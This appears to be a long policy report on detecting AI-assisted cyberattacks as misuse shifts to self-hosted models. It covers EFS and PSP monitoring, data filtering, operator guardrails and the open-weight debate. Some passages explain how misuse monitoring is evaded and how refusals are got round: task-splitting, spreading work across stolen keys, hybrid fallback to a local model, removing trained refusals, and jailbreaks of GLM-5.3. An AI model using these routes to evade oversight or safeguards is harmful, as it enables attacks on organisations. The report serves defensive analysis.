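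Other cases that sound like self-hosting also involve an outside host. Google Cloud reports that malware from APT28, a Russian state group, obtained its commands from a model through Hugging Face's API. SiliconANGLE's *Google warns that a new era of self-evolving, AI-driven malware has begun* (2025) identifies the models involved as open-source. Providers of closed models saw none of that traffic, but it still passed through a company that could examine it or cut it off. The February edition of Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* (2026) describes a supposedly independent model, on sale to criminals, that depended on commercial APIs.

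The trade in stolen keys also suggests that hosted models are still worth having. The Russian-speaking criminal who attacked 30 AI companies was trying to reach an unreleased Claude model and failed. Someone who could do equally good work on a local model would have had little reason to try. Ordinary stolen keys are weaker evidence, since an attacker might want them simply because somebody else pays for the computing.

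Capability is becoming less of an obstacle to using local models. According to a commentary in Lawfare, a publication on law and national security, a low-skilled attacker who used Claude Opus 4.5 and GPT-5.2 could now automate the work equally well with Qwen 3.6, which runs locally. This is a judgement about what is possible and doesn't show that attackers have switched. AISI, the British government's AI Security Institute, treats the gap between closed and open models as time for defenders to prepare before similar abilities become available without the same safeguards.

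Any count of attackers who self-host models will probably be too low. Providers can't see them, and victims' logs show commands and network connections but rarely which model produced them. Acronis' *BOSSAI* describes an operator who used a system of 12 AI agents against organisations in 11 countries, including Taiwan's emergency services. Because Acronis is a security company and doesn't run the models, its research can uncover campaigns that no provider has reported. To establish where the model ran, investigators usually need the attacker's server or configuration files, as in the exploit_agent case.

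### The arithmetic of lost visibility

Let s be the share of misuse that takes place entirely on self-hosted models, and d the fraction of the remaining misuse that providers catch. Providers then catch

(1 − s)d

of all misuse. Nobody knows the real values, but the formula shows how the two interact:

| | Providers catch 60% of what they can see (d = 0.6) | Providers catch 90% (d = 0.9) |
|---|---|---|
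| 20% of misuse is self-hosted (s = 0.2) | 0.48 | 0.72 |
| 70% of misuse is self-hosted (s = 0.7) | 0.18 | 0.27 |

If s rises from 0.2 to 0.7 while d stays at 0.6, total detection falls from 48% to 18%. Raising d to 0.9 brings it back to only 27%. Even perfect monitoring would catch no more than 30%, because the total can never exceed 1 − s. The improvement from 0.6 to 0.9 would fully offset the loss only until s reached

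1 − 0.48/0.9 ≈ 0.47

An attacker who uses both hosted and self-hosted models, like the operator of exploit_agent, does not count towards s, because the hosted part of the work can still reveal the operation. This is somewhat reassuring as long as mixed use remains common.

The formula treats s and d as independent, which they probably aren't. If the attackers who leave are mainly those whom providers have already caught and banned, d falls as s rises, because the ones who remain are harder to catch. If the most careful attackers leave first, d rises and the published results look better, even though providers no longer see the worst cases. The formula also gives a clumsy scam the same weight as an intrusion at a ministry, and it counts an attack as caught even if the provider noticed it only after the data was stolen.

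### Signals outside the provider

An attack still has to reach its target, whatever model directs it. Hugging Face's alert system flagged the break-in by OpenAI's agents before anyone knew whose agents they were. Network equipment can record unusual connections, and a victim can check its logs to see which accounts an intruder used and what data left. Google wrote in its November report that current attack frameworks "trade stealth for velocity" and leave recognisable traces in traffic and code. It expects them to become stealthier as the tools and models improve.

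These signals would have to do a lot of work to replace the providers' lost share. Suppose s is 0.7, d is 0.6 and others catch a fraction e of the self-hosted attacks. To get back from 18% to the original 48%, e would have to be

(0.48 − 0.18)/0.7 ≈ 0.43

This leaves out the hosted attacks that the same methods would catch anyway. Whether defenders can reach 43% depends partly on speed. CyberInsider, a security news site, reports that one criminal used a group of AI agents to build and launch a large credential-theft operation in under six hours. A company that reviews its logs weekly would find out about such an attack days later.

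Compute providers could also help with monitoring. An attacker who wants to run a large model but owns no GPUs has to rent them, and the provider knows who pays and how much capacity they use. It can also see which outside addresses the machines contact, usually without reading any prompts. But heavy GPU use looks much the same whether the customer is attacking a bank or defending one. Connections to victims may reveal more, and they often come from rented servers other than the GPU machines. One ShinyHunters affiliate, for example, ran a credential-harvesting system on ten of Amazon's cloud servers. Attackers who run a small model on their own hardware would not be visible to a GPU provider, but they might still rent servers for the attack.

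Victims and cloud companies mostly lack a view across targets. Anthropic could link some 30 targets through one set of accounts, whereas each victim sees one intrusion and may never learn that the same intruder attacked others. Governments can build this wider view if victims report what they find. On 13 November 2026 the FBI issued an alert about ARTEX, an open-source penetration-testing framework that attackers had used against organisations in finance, government, healthcare, energy and other sectors. According to Markovic, the attacks had been under way since at least August.

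## Hosted services that leave the data with the customer

Anthropic and OpenAI need stored traffic to find misuse that shows up only across many requests, but their most cautious customers want them to store nothing. Each company now offers a system in which the customer stores the text and the provider's software scans it. Anthropic announced Enterprise Frontier Safeguards (EFS) on 1 September 2026, after customers objected to its 30-day storage rule. The public beta began in late November, according to *Anthropic Expands Enterprise Safeguards for Detecting AI Misuse* (Kovacs, 2026). OpenAI previewed Private Safety Processing (PSP) on 19 August, and by late November its documentation listed PSP as an option for API customers.

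### How Enterprise Frontier Safeguards works

Suppose a thief steals a bank's API key for Claude and uses it to attack other companies. Claude answers every prompt that passes the classifier, and the prompts and replies go into storage that the bank rents from Amazon or Google. Once the text is there, neither Anthropic nor its cloud partners keep a copy, according to *Anthropic wants to catch rogue AI activity without retaining your data* (Pogorelec, 2026).

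The bank encrypts this text with its own key. Anthropic's *What are customer-managed encryption keys (CMEK)* explains how such keys work across its products. The customer creates the key in its cloud company's key service, and Anthropic's systems use it there. Every use appears in the customer's audit log, so the bank can check when Anthropic's software used the key.

That software reads a rolling window of the bank's traffic. It checks for attempts to develop cyber or biological weapons and for signs of stolen credentials. For example, it might detect that a key the bank normally uses to summarise loan documents in office hours is now being used to scan foreign networks at night. It also checks for AI agents that go beyond their instructions, for instance by exploiting a flaw to get into an internal database.

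When the software finds something, it creates a "Safety Case". The bank's security staff can fetch it from their own storage or through an API, and feed it into the system that collects their other alerts. A case contains no prompts or replies, so the staff must look up the conversations themselves. Nobody at Anthropic reviews them. Help Net Security's *Anthropic’s Enterprise Frontier Safeguards lets your Claude logs stay in your cloud* points out that the customer now has to staff the alert queue.

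Anthropic charges nothing for EFS, but the cloud provider bills the customer for storing, reading, writing and transferring the data. The bill could be noticeable for a team that uses agents, because agents resend a lot of text.

On Amazon's Bedrock and Google's managed service, the cloud company runs the safeguards and keeps the data in its own environment. Microsoft Foundry is not yet supported. Customers turn on their own storage, their own keys and fully automated review as separate settings. A client whose penetration tester claims to use EFS should therefore ask which of the three are on.

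### How Private Safety Processing works

OpenAI's system also scans text that the customer stores, but it sends each alert's category and severity to OpenAI, which uses them to decide whether to act against the account. Only the customer receives the full alert. A customer who disagrees with OpenAI's decision can appeal and choose to share the conversations.

The Next Web's *OpenAI previews Private Safety Processing to keep zero data retention* reports an example that Aleah Houze, OpenAI's head of product policy, gave at a press briefing. Someone asks about a weakness in a company's software in one conversation. In another, the same person asks about remote access and which security tools can detect it. Each conversation looks like ordinary research, but together they suggest an attack.

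They could equally suggest an investigation, because a responder may want to know which flaw the intruder used, how the intruder kept remote access and why no tool raised an alarm.

OpenAI promised a technical white paper for September. Its documentation now cites the paper, along with a set-up guide, and distinguishes three arrangements:

| Arrangement | Where the content lies | Whether OpenAI's staff may read it |
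|---|---|---|
| Zero data retention (ZDR) with PSP | Storage the customer controls | No |
| Private Retention with PSP | Encrypted logs on OpenAI's infrastructure | Only if the law requires it |
| Safety Retention | OpenAI may store content that its classifiers flag | Yes, if a classifier has flagged it |

OpenAI can move a customer from ZDR to Safety Retention only to investigate or prevent severe risks, but no such condition applies to Private Retention. OpenAI's systems could therefore store some text from a customer that chose PSP to keep all of it on its own systems.

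In its August preview, OpenAI promised that customers would control the keys to anything it stored for them. The documentation describes the Private Retention logs as encrypted and refers readers to an appendix of the white paper for details. A security team should confirm who holds the keys before relying on this arrangement.

### Who can read the text

In both systems, the provider's software can read the text. *Comparing OpenAI and Anthropic’s Data Retention Policies* notes that employees may be unable to see a prompt even though the company's systems can. The model has to read the prompt to answer it, and the review software has to decrypt the stored copy to scan it. An intruder who took over either one could read the text it processes.

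The main benefit is that the provider no longer holds a month of the customer's prompts, which a thief could steal or a court could demand. But as of early September, neither company had addressed whether someone suing the AI company could obtain logs stored on a customer's servers.

Anthropic also isn't allowed to train its models or classifiers on EFS content, so when a customer dismisses a false alarm, Anthropic can't use it as an example to correct the software.

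### When the customer is the attacker

EFS works well against the thief with the bank's key, because the bank has a strong incentive to act on the flag. It also works against a rogue employee, unless that employee reads the alerts. It works badly if the customer is a front company for an espionage group, because the attackers then receive the flag and learn that the software has recognised their pattern.

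Anthropic has other ways to notice such a customer. It still runs classifiers on individual requests, and under the ZDR terms of June 2026 it kept the results to enforce its usage policy, so a customer that triggered many blocks could attract attention. But the group that Anthropic caught in September 2025 had split its attacks into tasks that each looked harmless, and Anthropic's announcement of EFS describes no step at which the company itself learns of such a pattern. Anthropic does limit EFS to eligible organisations, which should keep out the crudest front companies.

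PSP handles this case better because OpenAI learns that a serious alert exists and can close the account without the customer's help. But OpenAI can't warn the victims, because the category and severity it receives don't identify them. Anthropic was able to notify organisations in 2025 because it could read the traffic.

OpenAI's power to suspend accounts is a problem for honest security firms. If PSP flags a penetration tester for attacking a network and OpenAI suspends the account, OpenAI can't read the conversations to confirm that the client gave permission. To win an appeal, the tester may have to hand over the client's data, which the contract may forbid. Under EFS, the tester's own firm would review the flag and dismiss it.

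Sanchit Vir Gogia, chief analyst at Greyhound Research, considers OpenAI's design workable but hard to verify, according to CBINEWS's *OpenAI新增AI安全层，在不保留企业数据的前提下检测滥用* (2026). Gogia says the provider keeps the alert while the customer keeps the case, and argues that zero retention shifts the work of investigation to the customer rather than eliminating it. A large bank has staff for this, but a ten-person testing firm may not.

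Attackers who spread their work across keys stolen from several customers are harder for both systems to detect, because each customer's storage would contain only part of the campaign. In their announcements, Anthropic and OpenAI both mention patterns across accounts, but neither explains whether its software compares different customers' accounts.

There appears to be no published independent test of how well either system detects misuse. Neither company had published an independent audit of its system's design by early September. On 16 November, OpenAI's *Our first phase of embedded assessments* announced that METR, Apollo Research, Transluce and Goodfire would evaluate its models' alignment, its safeguards and its monitoring systems. That work may eventually cover PSP. In a convincing test, outsiders would imitate known campaigns through approved accounts and measure how many the software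 flagged, how quickly it flagged them, and how often it flagged ordinary defensive work.

### Confidential computing

Confidential computing could let customers check some of these promises. It relies on a trusted execution environment (TEE), a protected area inside a processor that shuts out even someone with full control of the machine. *Private AI* (Sun and Guzzo, 2026) describes its two parts as hardware isolation and a report signed by the hardware.

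A prompt would travel through such a system in this order:

1. The processor encrypts everything in the protected memory with a key that stays inside the chip. An administrator who copies the memory gets unreadable data.
2. The processor calculates a fingerprint of the software it has loaded into the protected area and signs it with another key built into the chip. This signed report is called an attestation.
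3. The customer's software checks the signature and compares the fingerprint with the one it expects. If even one line of the provider's program has changed, the two won't match.
4. If they match, the customer's software encrypts the prompt so that only the program in the protected area can open it.

*Private AI clouds are the future of inference* describes two consumer services that already use this approach. Apple sends demanding tasks from its devices to Private Cloud Compute, and Meta built Private Processing for WhatsApp.

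Safety checks can run inside the protected area too. In *Improving Safety with Privacy*, Tetali, who leads OpenAI's work on privacy-preserving infrastructure, argues that encryption and attestation can support strong guardrails without routine human access to users' data. The launch announcements for EFS and PSP don't mention confidential computing, so customers can't assume from them that either system offers this protection.

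An attestation proves which program is running, but not that the program is safe. A program that copies every prompt to a log can still have a valid attestation, so someone the customer trusts has to inspect the code. *OpenPcc* (2026) finds the privacy of Google's Private AI Compute hard to verify because the code is closed and Google offers no copy of the finished program to inspect. It also says that Anthropic's white paper on confidential computing gives only a high-level overview, without a system that others could deploy.

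Every software update changes the fingerprint, so somebody has to inspect the new version before customers can trust it. This makes it harder for a provider to fix a flaw within hours. Tetali also lists appeals and incidents among the open problems. An engineer can't easily find out why a system failed if the hardware hides what the system was doing.

The hardware has weaknesses too. Researchers have recovered secrets from several generations of these chips, some by timing operations and others by attaching equipment to the memory. A cloud company has physical access to its machines, so the protection is weakest against a company determined to break it. It is much stronger against a curious employee or an intruder who breaks in over the network.

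A cryptographic alternative, which relies less on hardware, can split the computation among several parties so that none of them sees the whole prompt. But *OpenPcc* describes TEEs as far more practical, and SPRINT, a recent cryptographic system, requires extra model training before use.

### Closed models on the customer's premises

A developer can also install a closed model in the customer's building. Google and Microsoft offer AI on systems with no outside connection. Prompts, credentials and logs then stay with the customer, as they do with a self-hosted open-weight model.

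The developer mainly worries that the weights will be stolen, because a customer who copied them could run the model without paying or remove its safeguards. Confidential computing can also protect the developer from the customer, by hiding the weights in a protected area of the customer's own machine. But the customer has unlimited physical access to that machine, so a developer might reasonably offer only its older models this way.

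The model still has its trained refusals and any classifier that the developer installs with it. A developer that can't see the traffic may want stricter guardrails, because it would have no other way to limit misuse.

An installed copy would probably keep working after an order like the one that shut off Fable 5 in June, unless its licence software has to contact the developer regularly. New installations abroad could be more vulnerable to such an order than a hosted service, because export rules clearly cover the weights. A hospital in Lyon could keep its current model but be unable to get the next version.

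### Open models on rented machines

David Bianco of Cisco Talos names Baseten and Together AI as options for teams that would rather rent a server than buy one, and says neither adds its own refusals to a customer's model. Teams can pick a model that refuses little, decide what to log, and move the same weights to another supplier if the first one closes their account.

The supplier still controls the hardware. *OpenPcc* proposes to reduce this problem by running open models inside TEEs on widely available processors. An open model suits this design because outsiders can both inspect the serving software and check the fingerprint of the weights. Renting such a machine may be the closest a team can get to self-hosting without owning the hardware.

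### The hybrid fallback and a model shared by an industry

In Bianco's hybrid design, a local model handles the prompts that a hosted model refuses. This lets a team use the strongest model for most of its work and buy less hardware. The two models may respond to the same prompt differently, so the team has to test its prompts on both. The team also has to maintain two systems.

The gateway first has to recognise a refusal. That is easy when the API labels it, but models sometimes refuse by giving vague advice, which software can miss. Software can also count useful replies as refusals, as it did in the study by Campbell and colleagues.

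This design doesn't protect confidential material, because the provider has already received any prompt it refuses. Hugging Face's responders had the same problem when they tried Claude first. A gateway could instead sort prompts before sending anything, and keep raw evidence and unpublished exploits on the local model. The local model would then have to be good enough for the team's most sensitive work, so the team may still have to buy a large server.

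Bianco calls sharing a model across an industry "collective inference". Companies in many industries already share warnings about attacks through joint organisations. Bianco suggests building on these organisations, perhaps with a model tuned to the attacks their members face.

Banks have already agreed on some of the rules such a model would need. Eight members of the Analysis and Resilience Center, an industry group that includes the largest American banks, worked with Anthropic on the requirements for EFS. They settled who holds the data and the keys, and when a person may look at the content. Sharing a server would require more trust, because the members compete and their evidence would pass through the same machine. Ibrahim and colleagues showed how one user of a shared server could load another's saved conversation.

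### Which reasons for self-hosting remain

The table compares each option with an ordinary hosted API that stores prompts for 30 days. "Removed" means the option largely eliminates this reason for self-hosting.

| Option | Confidentiality | Credentials | Logs | Jurisdiction | Refusals |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EFS with all three parts on | Reduced | Reduced | Removed | Unchanged | Unchanged |
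| PSP with the customer's storage | Reduced | Reduced | Removed | Unchanged | Unchanged |
| Closed model in a TEE, with code the customer can check | Removed | Removed | Removed, if the code stores nothing | Reduced | Unchanged |
| Closed model on the customer's premises | Removed | Removed | Removed | Reduced | Unchanged |
| Open model on rented dedicated machines | Reduced | Reduced | Removed | Reduced | Removed |
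| Hybrid that falls back after a refusal | Unchanged | Unchanged | Unchanged | Reduced | Removed |
| Model shared by an industry | Reduced | Reduced | Reduced | Reduced | Removed |

The table's "Jurisdiction" heading covers both the risk of disclosure and the risk of losing the model. A TEE makes disclosure harder but doesn't stop a government from having the service switched off. With a hybrid, the local model keeps working after a shutdown, but the provider can still disclose what it has stored. EFS may do little for a European customer because an American cloud company runs both the storage and the key service.

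EFS and PSP would not have helped Hugging Face, whose problem was refusals. Anthropic states that EFS leaves the model's behaviour unchanged. A team that wants to address both refusals and logs also needs verified access, and OpenAI allows that combination for GPT-6 Cyber. A bank that obtains both the data protection and verified access before a break-in has much less reason to buy its own server. A tester whose client forbids any outside processing must use the customer's own hardware, where a closed model may still refuse to write the exploit.

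## Which guardrails survive a download

A team that downloads an open-weight model gets the guardrails built into the weights, but not those that run on the developer's servers.

| Guardrail | Does it come with the weights? | Can the operator drop it? | Can the developer correct it later? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Filtering of the training data | Yes | Only by supplying the missing knowledge | Only by releasing a new model |
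| Trained refusals | Yes | Yes | Only by releasing a new model |
| Classifiers around the model | No, though some developers offer one as a separate download | Yes | Yes on its own service; elsewhere only if the operator installs the update |
| Account rules, such as identity checks and bans | No | A local copy needs no account | Yes for its own customers, but not for downloaded copies |
| Law | It applies to people and organisations rather than to files | Not legally | No, that is up to legislators and courts |

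People can remove trained refusals from open weights, and thousands of models without them already exist, as Casper, O'Brien and colleagues report in *Open Technical Problems in Open-Weight AI Model Risk Management* (2026). *Frontier Open-Weight AI Risk Management Framework* (Tse, Galeev and colleagues, 2026) warns that adapting a model to harmless work can also weaken its safeguards by accident, so teams should test a model again after customising it. Some of the framework's contributors work for Z.ai, the developer of GLM-5.2.

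Developers have much less power to correct mistakes after an open release. In April 2025 OpenAI restored an earlier version of GPT-4o after outsiders found that an update flattered users and encouraged self-harm. It could not have done the same with gpt-oss-120b, an open-weight model that people were downloading more than three million times a month. A developer can publish a corrected model, but Tse and colleagues point out that this helps only if users adopt it. Many owners of Ollama servers don't even install security fixes.

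The same model can therefore have different guardrails depending on where it runs. *Kimi K3 Safety Audit* (Agarwal, 2026) tested Kimi K3 on its developer's service, where a filter was active, and on another company's machines, where the official weights ran without one.

### Filtering the training data

A model that refuses a request may still contain the information needed to answer it. With data filtering, the developer removes text about a subject before training, so the model has little chance to learn it.

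In the main experiment, reported in *Deep Ignorance* (2025), O'Brien, Casper and colleagues trained several models with 6.9 billion weights from scratch on 550 billion tokens. One model saw all the text, while others saw text without material related to biological weapons. The researchers then tested what the models had learned with exam questions on related but harmless biology.

Their filter first compared every document with a list of biological terms. More than 90% of documents contained fewer than two of these terms and went straight into the training data. The strong version of the filter discarded the rest, about 8% of documents in the main training stage and 9% in a shorter final stage. In the weak version, a classifier checked these documents in the final stage and let nearly half of them through. Filtering used less than 1% as much computation as training.

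Always choosing the longest of the four answers was correct on 46% of the exam questions, so O'Brien and colleagues dropped questions that other models could answer from the options alone. They also ran a harder test in which the model never saw the options together. The filtered models did no better than chance on that test and showed no decline in general abilities.

The researchers then tried to put the knowledge back by training the models on biothreat-related text. The filtered models still showed substantial resistance after 10,000 training steps and about 300 million tokens. Safeguards that developers add after the main training had typically failed within several hundred steps. Further training on unrelated text didn't restore the knowledge.

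But the filtered models could use dangerous information given in the prompt. They answered well when O'Brien and colleagues included a scientific abstract that contained the answer. An agent that can search the web could therefore find much of what its model never learned, although a person could search for it too.

The resistance to retraining also has limits. O'Brien and colleagues acknowledge that 300 million tokens is not very much, and their attempts took about 17 hours on two GPUs. They expect attackers to have more trouble collecting good training material than running the retraining. The documents and questions O'Brien's team used had cost other researchers more than $200,000 to prepare.

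Filtering training data also seems to work better on knowledge than on behaviour. Models trained without toxic text have not been consistently harder to misuse. O'Brien and colleagues suspect this is because precise scientific facts come from a small set of documents, whereas a model needs no special knowledge to be abusive or to try to help with a harmful request.

### What later experiments found

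Results since then have been mixed. Casper and colleagues cite a test on gpt-oss in which filtering was ineffective. They conclude that filtering works best when developers remove a whole field of science or engineering, and less well when they remove a narrow topic.

*Shaping capabilities with token-level data filtering* (Rathi and Radford, 2026) made the filter more precise by removing individual tokens, so a medical phrase could be cut from a news article while the rest stayed. The experiments used medical knowledge as a stand-in for dangerous knowledge, and the largest model had 1.8 billion weights. An unfiltered model needed only about one seven-thousandth of the training computation to predict medical text as well as that token-filtered model, compared with about one thirtieth to match a model trained with whole documents removed. Both methods became more effective as the models grew,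 which is encouraging because leading models are far larger. The token-filtered model was also easier to teach to refuse medical questions, so a developer can combine filtering with trained refusals.

*DETER* (Glarou and Jaggi, 2026) reports less reassuring results on how long the effect of filtering lasts. Glarou and Jaggi filtered medical text out of the training data for models with up to a billion weights, then trained the models on medical articles. The largest model needed only about 100,000 tokens of these articles to predict such text as well as a model trained on unfiltered data.

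Glarou and Jaggi also tested a stronger method. After every 50 ordinary training steps, they added a step that made the model worse at predicting some of the removed text. Restoring the largest model's performance then took 2.09 million tokens, about 20 times as many. They call both amounts small, since even the larger one is only 0.01% of the model's original training text.

These numbers look far worse than the 300 million tokens in O'Brien and colleagues' experiment, but they measure something different. A model may get better at predicting medical articles just by picking up their vocabulary and style, whereas O'Brien and colleagues tested knowledge of specific facts, in models about seven times larger. None of these experiments removed hacking knowledge.

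### Moonshot's Kimi K3.1 Pro

The Chinese company Moonshot AI announced Kimi K3.1 Pro in October 2026. According to AsiaOne's *Moonshot curbs hacking ability in new Kimi model as fears grow over* (2026), the company removed cyber-related data from the training text and from the simulated tasks the model practises on, but kept its general coding skills.

Moonshot measured the effect with an internal test of finding and exploiting software flaws. K3.1 Pro scored 81%, compared with 90.5% for a similar version without these measures. Its predecessor, Kimi K3, had scored 33%, as Constantin reports in *Moonshot releases Kimi K3.1 Pro and says it cut its hacking skills* (2026). The share of the improvement that filtering removed was therefore

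(90.5 − 81)/(90.5 − 33) ≈ 17%

so the released model kept about five-sixths of the gain.

The effect was probably modest partly because Moonshot started from an existing model. Its Kimi blog describes K3.1 Pro as a version of K3 with much more of the later training, and filtering that later training can't remove what K3 had already learned. Exploiting a flaw also draws on general programming skill, which Moonshot wanted to improve.

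Moonshot says it aims to avoid releasing weights that would "extend the absolute frontier of cyber capability". Under that standard, the limit is the strongest model anywhere, open or closed. K3.1 Pro could stay within that limit and still be much more useful than K3 to attackers who depend on open weights.

K3's trained refusals offered little protection. The *UK AISI / CAISI Preliminary Assessment of Kimi K3's Cyber Capabilities* (2026) examined its hacking ability. TechInformed's *Open weight AI model Kimi K3 completes simulated network attack* reports that K3's safeguards did not prevent it from attempting exploit development or offensive operations. But K3 failed to run its own commands in any of 41 tasks involving flaws in the Chrome browser's JavaScript engine, while the best comparison models succeeded in 20 on average. K3's limited skill was therefore a stronger barrier than its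 refusals, but K3.1 Pro is much more skilled.

### What filtering costs defenders

K3.1 Pro's 9.5-point loss would also make it less useful to a software maker looking for flaws in its own product. Moonshot itself argues that open-weight models help more organisations inspect and secure their software, including old systems that get little attention.

A hosted provider can reduce this drawback by loosening its classifiers for verified customers, but a filtered open-weight model is the same for everyone who downloads it. Moonshot could offer approved defenders the unfiltered version through an API, but they would have to send Moonshot their prompts.

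Defensive and offensive knowledge are also hard to separate. *MiST* (2026) describes training models for security work on catalogues of attackers' techniques, alongside countermeasures and detection rules. Filtering out the catalogues would remove much of what an analyst needs to write a detection rule.

*Mark, Don't Erase* (2026) proposes putting a special marker before hazardous sentences instead of deleting them. General text alone was enough to preserve the model's other knowledge in the biology case, but for cybersecurity the researchers had to add 4,173 security documents because the model was otherwise likely to refuse harmless questions.

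Casper and colleagues consider it an open question whether filtering can limit offensive hacking without harming defence. Zhuo, Ding and colleagues (2026), in *To Defend Against Cyber Attacks, We Must Teach AI Agents to Hack*, doubt that filtering can do much to limit hacking. They argue that many attacks come from reasoning about a system rather than from remembered exploits, and that agents can look up what they don't know. They also think defenders need offensive AI to predict how attackers will behave. The drop in K3.1 Pro's score shows that filtering reduces hacking skill somewhat, but most of the skill remained.

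How much filtering limits a user depends on the task. A responder reading a log to find out what happened can put a recent threat report in the prompt, since O'Brien and colleagues found that filtered models can use information supplied there. A vulnerability researcher may lose more, because Moonshot also removed practice tasks, and a document in the prompt probably can't replace practice.

### Guardrails the operator can add

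An organisation that hosts its own model can put guardrails around it, but it has to decide what counts as misuse and write the policy, which a hosted provider would otherwise do for all its customers. The organisation is also responsible if it gets the policy wrong.

A local classifier is the closest substitute for the provider's classifier. A general-purpose one would probably flag the same malware and exploits that cause refusals on hosted services, but the team can choose the threshold, see every blocked request and exempt particular analysts. A narrower classifier, such as one that looks for instructions hidden in evidence, may be more useful.

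Limits on tools are more dependable because they work whatever the model writes. A penetration-testing firm can build a scanner that accepts only the addresses in the client's contract. A hosted classifier would have to guess whether the tester has permission, but this scanner can check. The firm's policy for its agents might look like this invented example:

| What the agent tries to do | Rule |
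|---|---|
| Run a suspicious program on an isolated lab machine | Allow and record |
| Scan an address listed in the contract | Allow during the agreed hours |
| Scan any other address | Block |
| Run an exploit on the client's live system | Ask the lead tester |
| Delete or change the client's data | Block |

For requests that such rules don't settle, the firm could borrow a method from *A Content-Based Framework for Cybersecurity Refusal Decisions in Large Language Models*. The firm would list the attacks that an answer could plausibly support, then estimate how much the answer would raise each attack's chance of success and how much harm the attack would do. An explanation of old malware would score low on both, while a working exploit for an unpatched flaw in widely used software would score high.

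Approval steps take time, and a lead tester who has to approve 200 actions a day will approve many of them without thinking. The firm should therefore require approval only for actions that could damage a live system.

All these guardrails protect mainly against mistakes and misled agents. The administrator can switch them off, and an attacker who runs the same model won't install them. To make insider abuse harder, the firm can send the audit log to someone outside the testing team and require a second person to approve policy changes. Zhuo and colleagues recommend confining offensive agents to audited cyber ranges, practice networks separate from real targets. Developers would then use the findings to train agents that can only defend.

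### What the law requires of developers and operators

Two new American AI safety laws place their main duties on frontier developers with more than $500 million in annual revenue. California's SB 53 has been in force since January 2026, and New York's RAISE Act takes effect on 1 January 2027. Both require these companies to publish a safety framework and report critical safety incidents, within 15 days in California and 72 hours in New York. A hospital that only runs GLM-5.2 is not such a developer, so neither law requires it to keep the model's refusals or install a classifier.

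The EU's AI Act also applies to operators, but it imposes few duties on most security teams. It distinguishes providers, who develop a model or system and put it on the market, from deployers, who use an AI system under their own authority. Providers of general-purpose models must document them, and providers of the most powerful ones must also assess and reduce systemic risks. A free and open-source licence exempts a provider from some of the documentation, but not from the systemic-risk duties.

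The hospital would normally be a deployer. It could become a provider by modifying the model heavily, but the European Commission's guidelines set the usual threshold at a third of the computation used to train the original, far more than any ordinary security team would use.

Most of the Act's duties for deployers concern "high-risk" uses, such as running critical infrastructure or hiring. Deployers of high-risk systems must follow the provider's instructions, assign competent people to oversee the system and keep its logs for at least six months. According to the Act's preamble, components used only for cybersecurity don't count as safety components of critical infrastructure, so a model that sorts alerts usually wouldn't be high-risk. It could be if it also used those alerts to evaluate employees' behaviour.

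Older laws matter more to most operators than AI laws do. Breaking into a computer without permission is a crime in most countries, whichever model wrote the exploit. If a hospital's model server leaks patients' data, EU data protection law generally gives the hospital 72 hours to notify the regulator. A penetration tester's contract may impose stricter rules than any AI law.

Developers can also set conditions through the licence. GLM-5.2's licence allows almost any use. Moonshot wrote its own licence for K3.1 Pro, and *Kimi K3 weights are open (with an asterisk)* (2026) describes the licence for K3 as restrictive. A law-abiding company has to read such terms before it uses the model. Enforcing them is harder, because the developer first has to discover a breach.

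In October 2026 China proposed banning exports of AI technology that generates malware and restricting exports of AI tools for finding software flaws. If the final rules cover published weights, the Chinese developers Moonshot and Z.ai might have to filter future models more heavily or keep some of them closed.

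## What the shift adds to the dispute over open and closed models

Hugging Face's account of the refusals quickly became evidence in an older dispute about whether developers should publish the weights of capable models. On 24 July 2026, eight days after the disclosure, Nvidia, Microsoft, Meta and 22 other signers published a letter defending open-weight AI, according to Constantin's *Nvidia, Microsoft, Meta back open AI. OpenAI didn't* (2026). They warned against "premature restrictions", TechRadar reports in *OpenAI quietly signs letter from Nvidia, Microsoft, and Meta*. OpenAI and Google signed later, but Anthropic had not signed by 28 July. By then, dozens of companies led by Nvidia had also formed the Open Secure AI Alliance to build open-source AI tools for defenders.

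AI safety advocates, by contrast, concluded that anyone with enough computing power might soon be able to run a similar attack, as Perrigo reports in *The OpenAI Hack Is Fueling a New Fight Over Open-Source AI* (2026). OpenAI's closed models had carried out the attack, but most observers put open-weight models only three to six months behind.

Many companies aren't clearly on the open or the closed side. OpenAI signed the letter and has released open weights, but it also runs a verified access programme for its closed models.

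### The case for open release

Supporters of open release want defenders to have at least one capable model that no provider can withhold, monitor or withdraw. Even some who worry about open weights accept much of this. AISI's *How Far Behind the Frontier are Leading Open Weight Models on Cyber?* lists private hosting and a dependable base "that providers can't change or deprecate" among the benefits.

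In The Next Web's *Open-weight AI caught the frontier on capability. On safety, it didn’t*, Clem Delangue, who runs Hugging Face, claims that the systems that stop one attack can stop millions more.

Others argue that open weights do less harm than their critics expect. Their usual test case is Claude Mythos Preview, which Anthropic gave only to selected partners in April because it could build sophisticated exploits on its own. Nathan Lambert, who writes a newsletter about AI models, claimed this autumn that the world would have been "more or less fine" if Anthropic had accidentally released the model's weights. In *Was I wrong about open models & cyber risks?* (2026), Lambert largely stands by this claim but admits to being nervous about it, and now expects an expensive period of repair for which he thinks "fine" may be the wrong word.

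Joshua Saxe made a related argument on 1 July, before the Hugging Face break-in, in *Restrictive AI cyber policy around both closed and open models* (Saxe, 2026). Saxe argues that because attackers can already download strong models, remove their safeguards and train them further for hacking, holding back new models mainly deprives defenders. Saxe wants American companies to release open weights more aggressively and to offer their best closed models widely, with monitoring.

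### The case for restricting the most capable weights

The main argument for restricting open-weight models is that nobody can undo a release. A developer that publishes weights permanently gives up the power to monitor users, ban them or withdraw the model. For models with dangerous abilities, AISI calls the result a "persistent and irreversible risk of misuse". AISI doesn't call for a ban, and describes the problem as balancing this risk against real benefits.

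Anthropic's researchers supplied the most specific evidence in September. In *GLM-5.3 and the spread of advanced cyber capabilities*, Fasano, Fleischer and colleagues (2026) used simple techniques to bypass the safeguards of GLM-5.3, the successor to the model Hugging Face used. The techniques worked between 64% and 100% of the time in simulated tests, but failed against Claude models with safeguards. The researchers conclude that GLM-5.3's lax safeguards "significantly increase the cyber capabilities available to malicious actors", but add that defenders can benefit too.

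Anthropic, which competes with Z.ai, ran the test in which Claude resisted such attacks, and not all closed models resist them as well. The non-profit Far.ai found hundreds of jailbreaks that work on many kinds of request when it tested xAI's Grok 4.5 and Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro, according to The Next Web. But xAI and Google can fix those models for everyone. The title of an October CBS News article, *Open-weight AI models are more vulnerable to manipulation and can lack oversight*, presents both problems as general weaknesses of open weights. According to the article, researchers see China's embrace of open weights as closing the gap with the United States.

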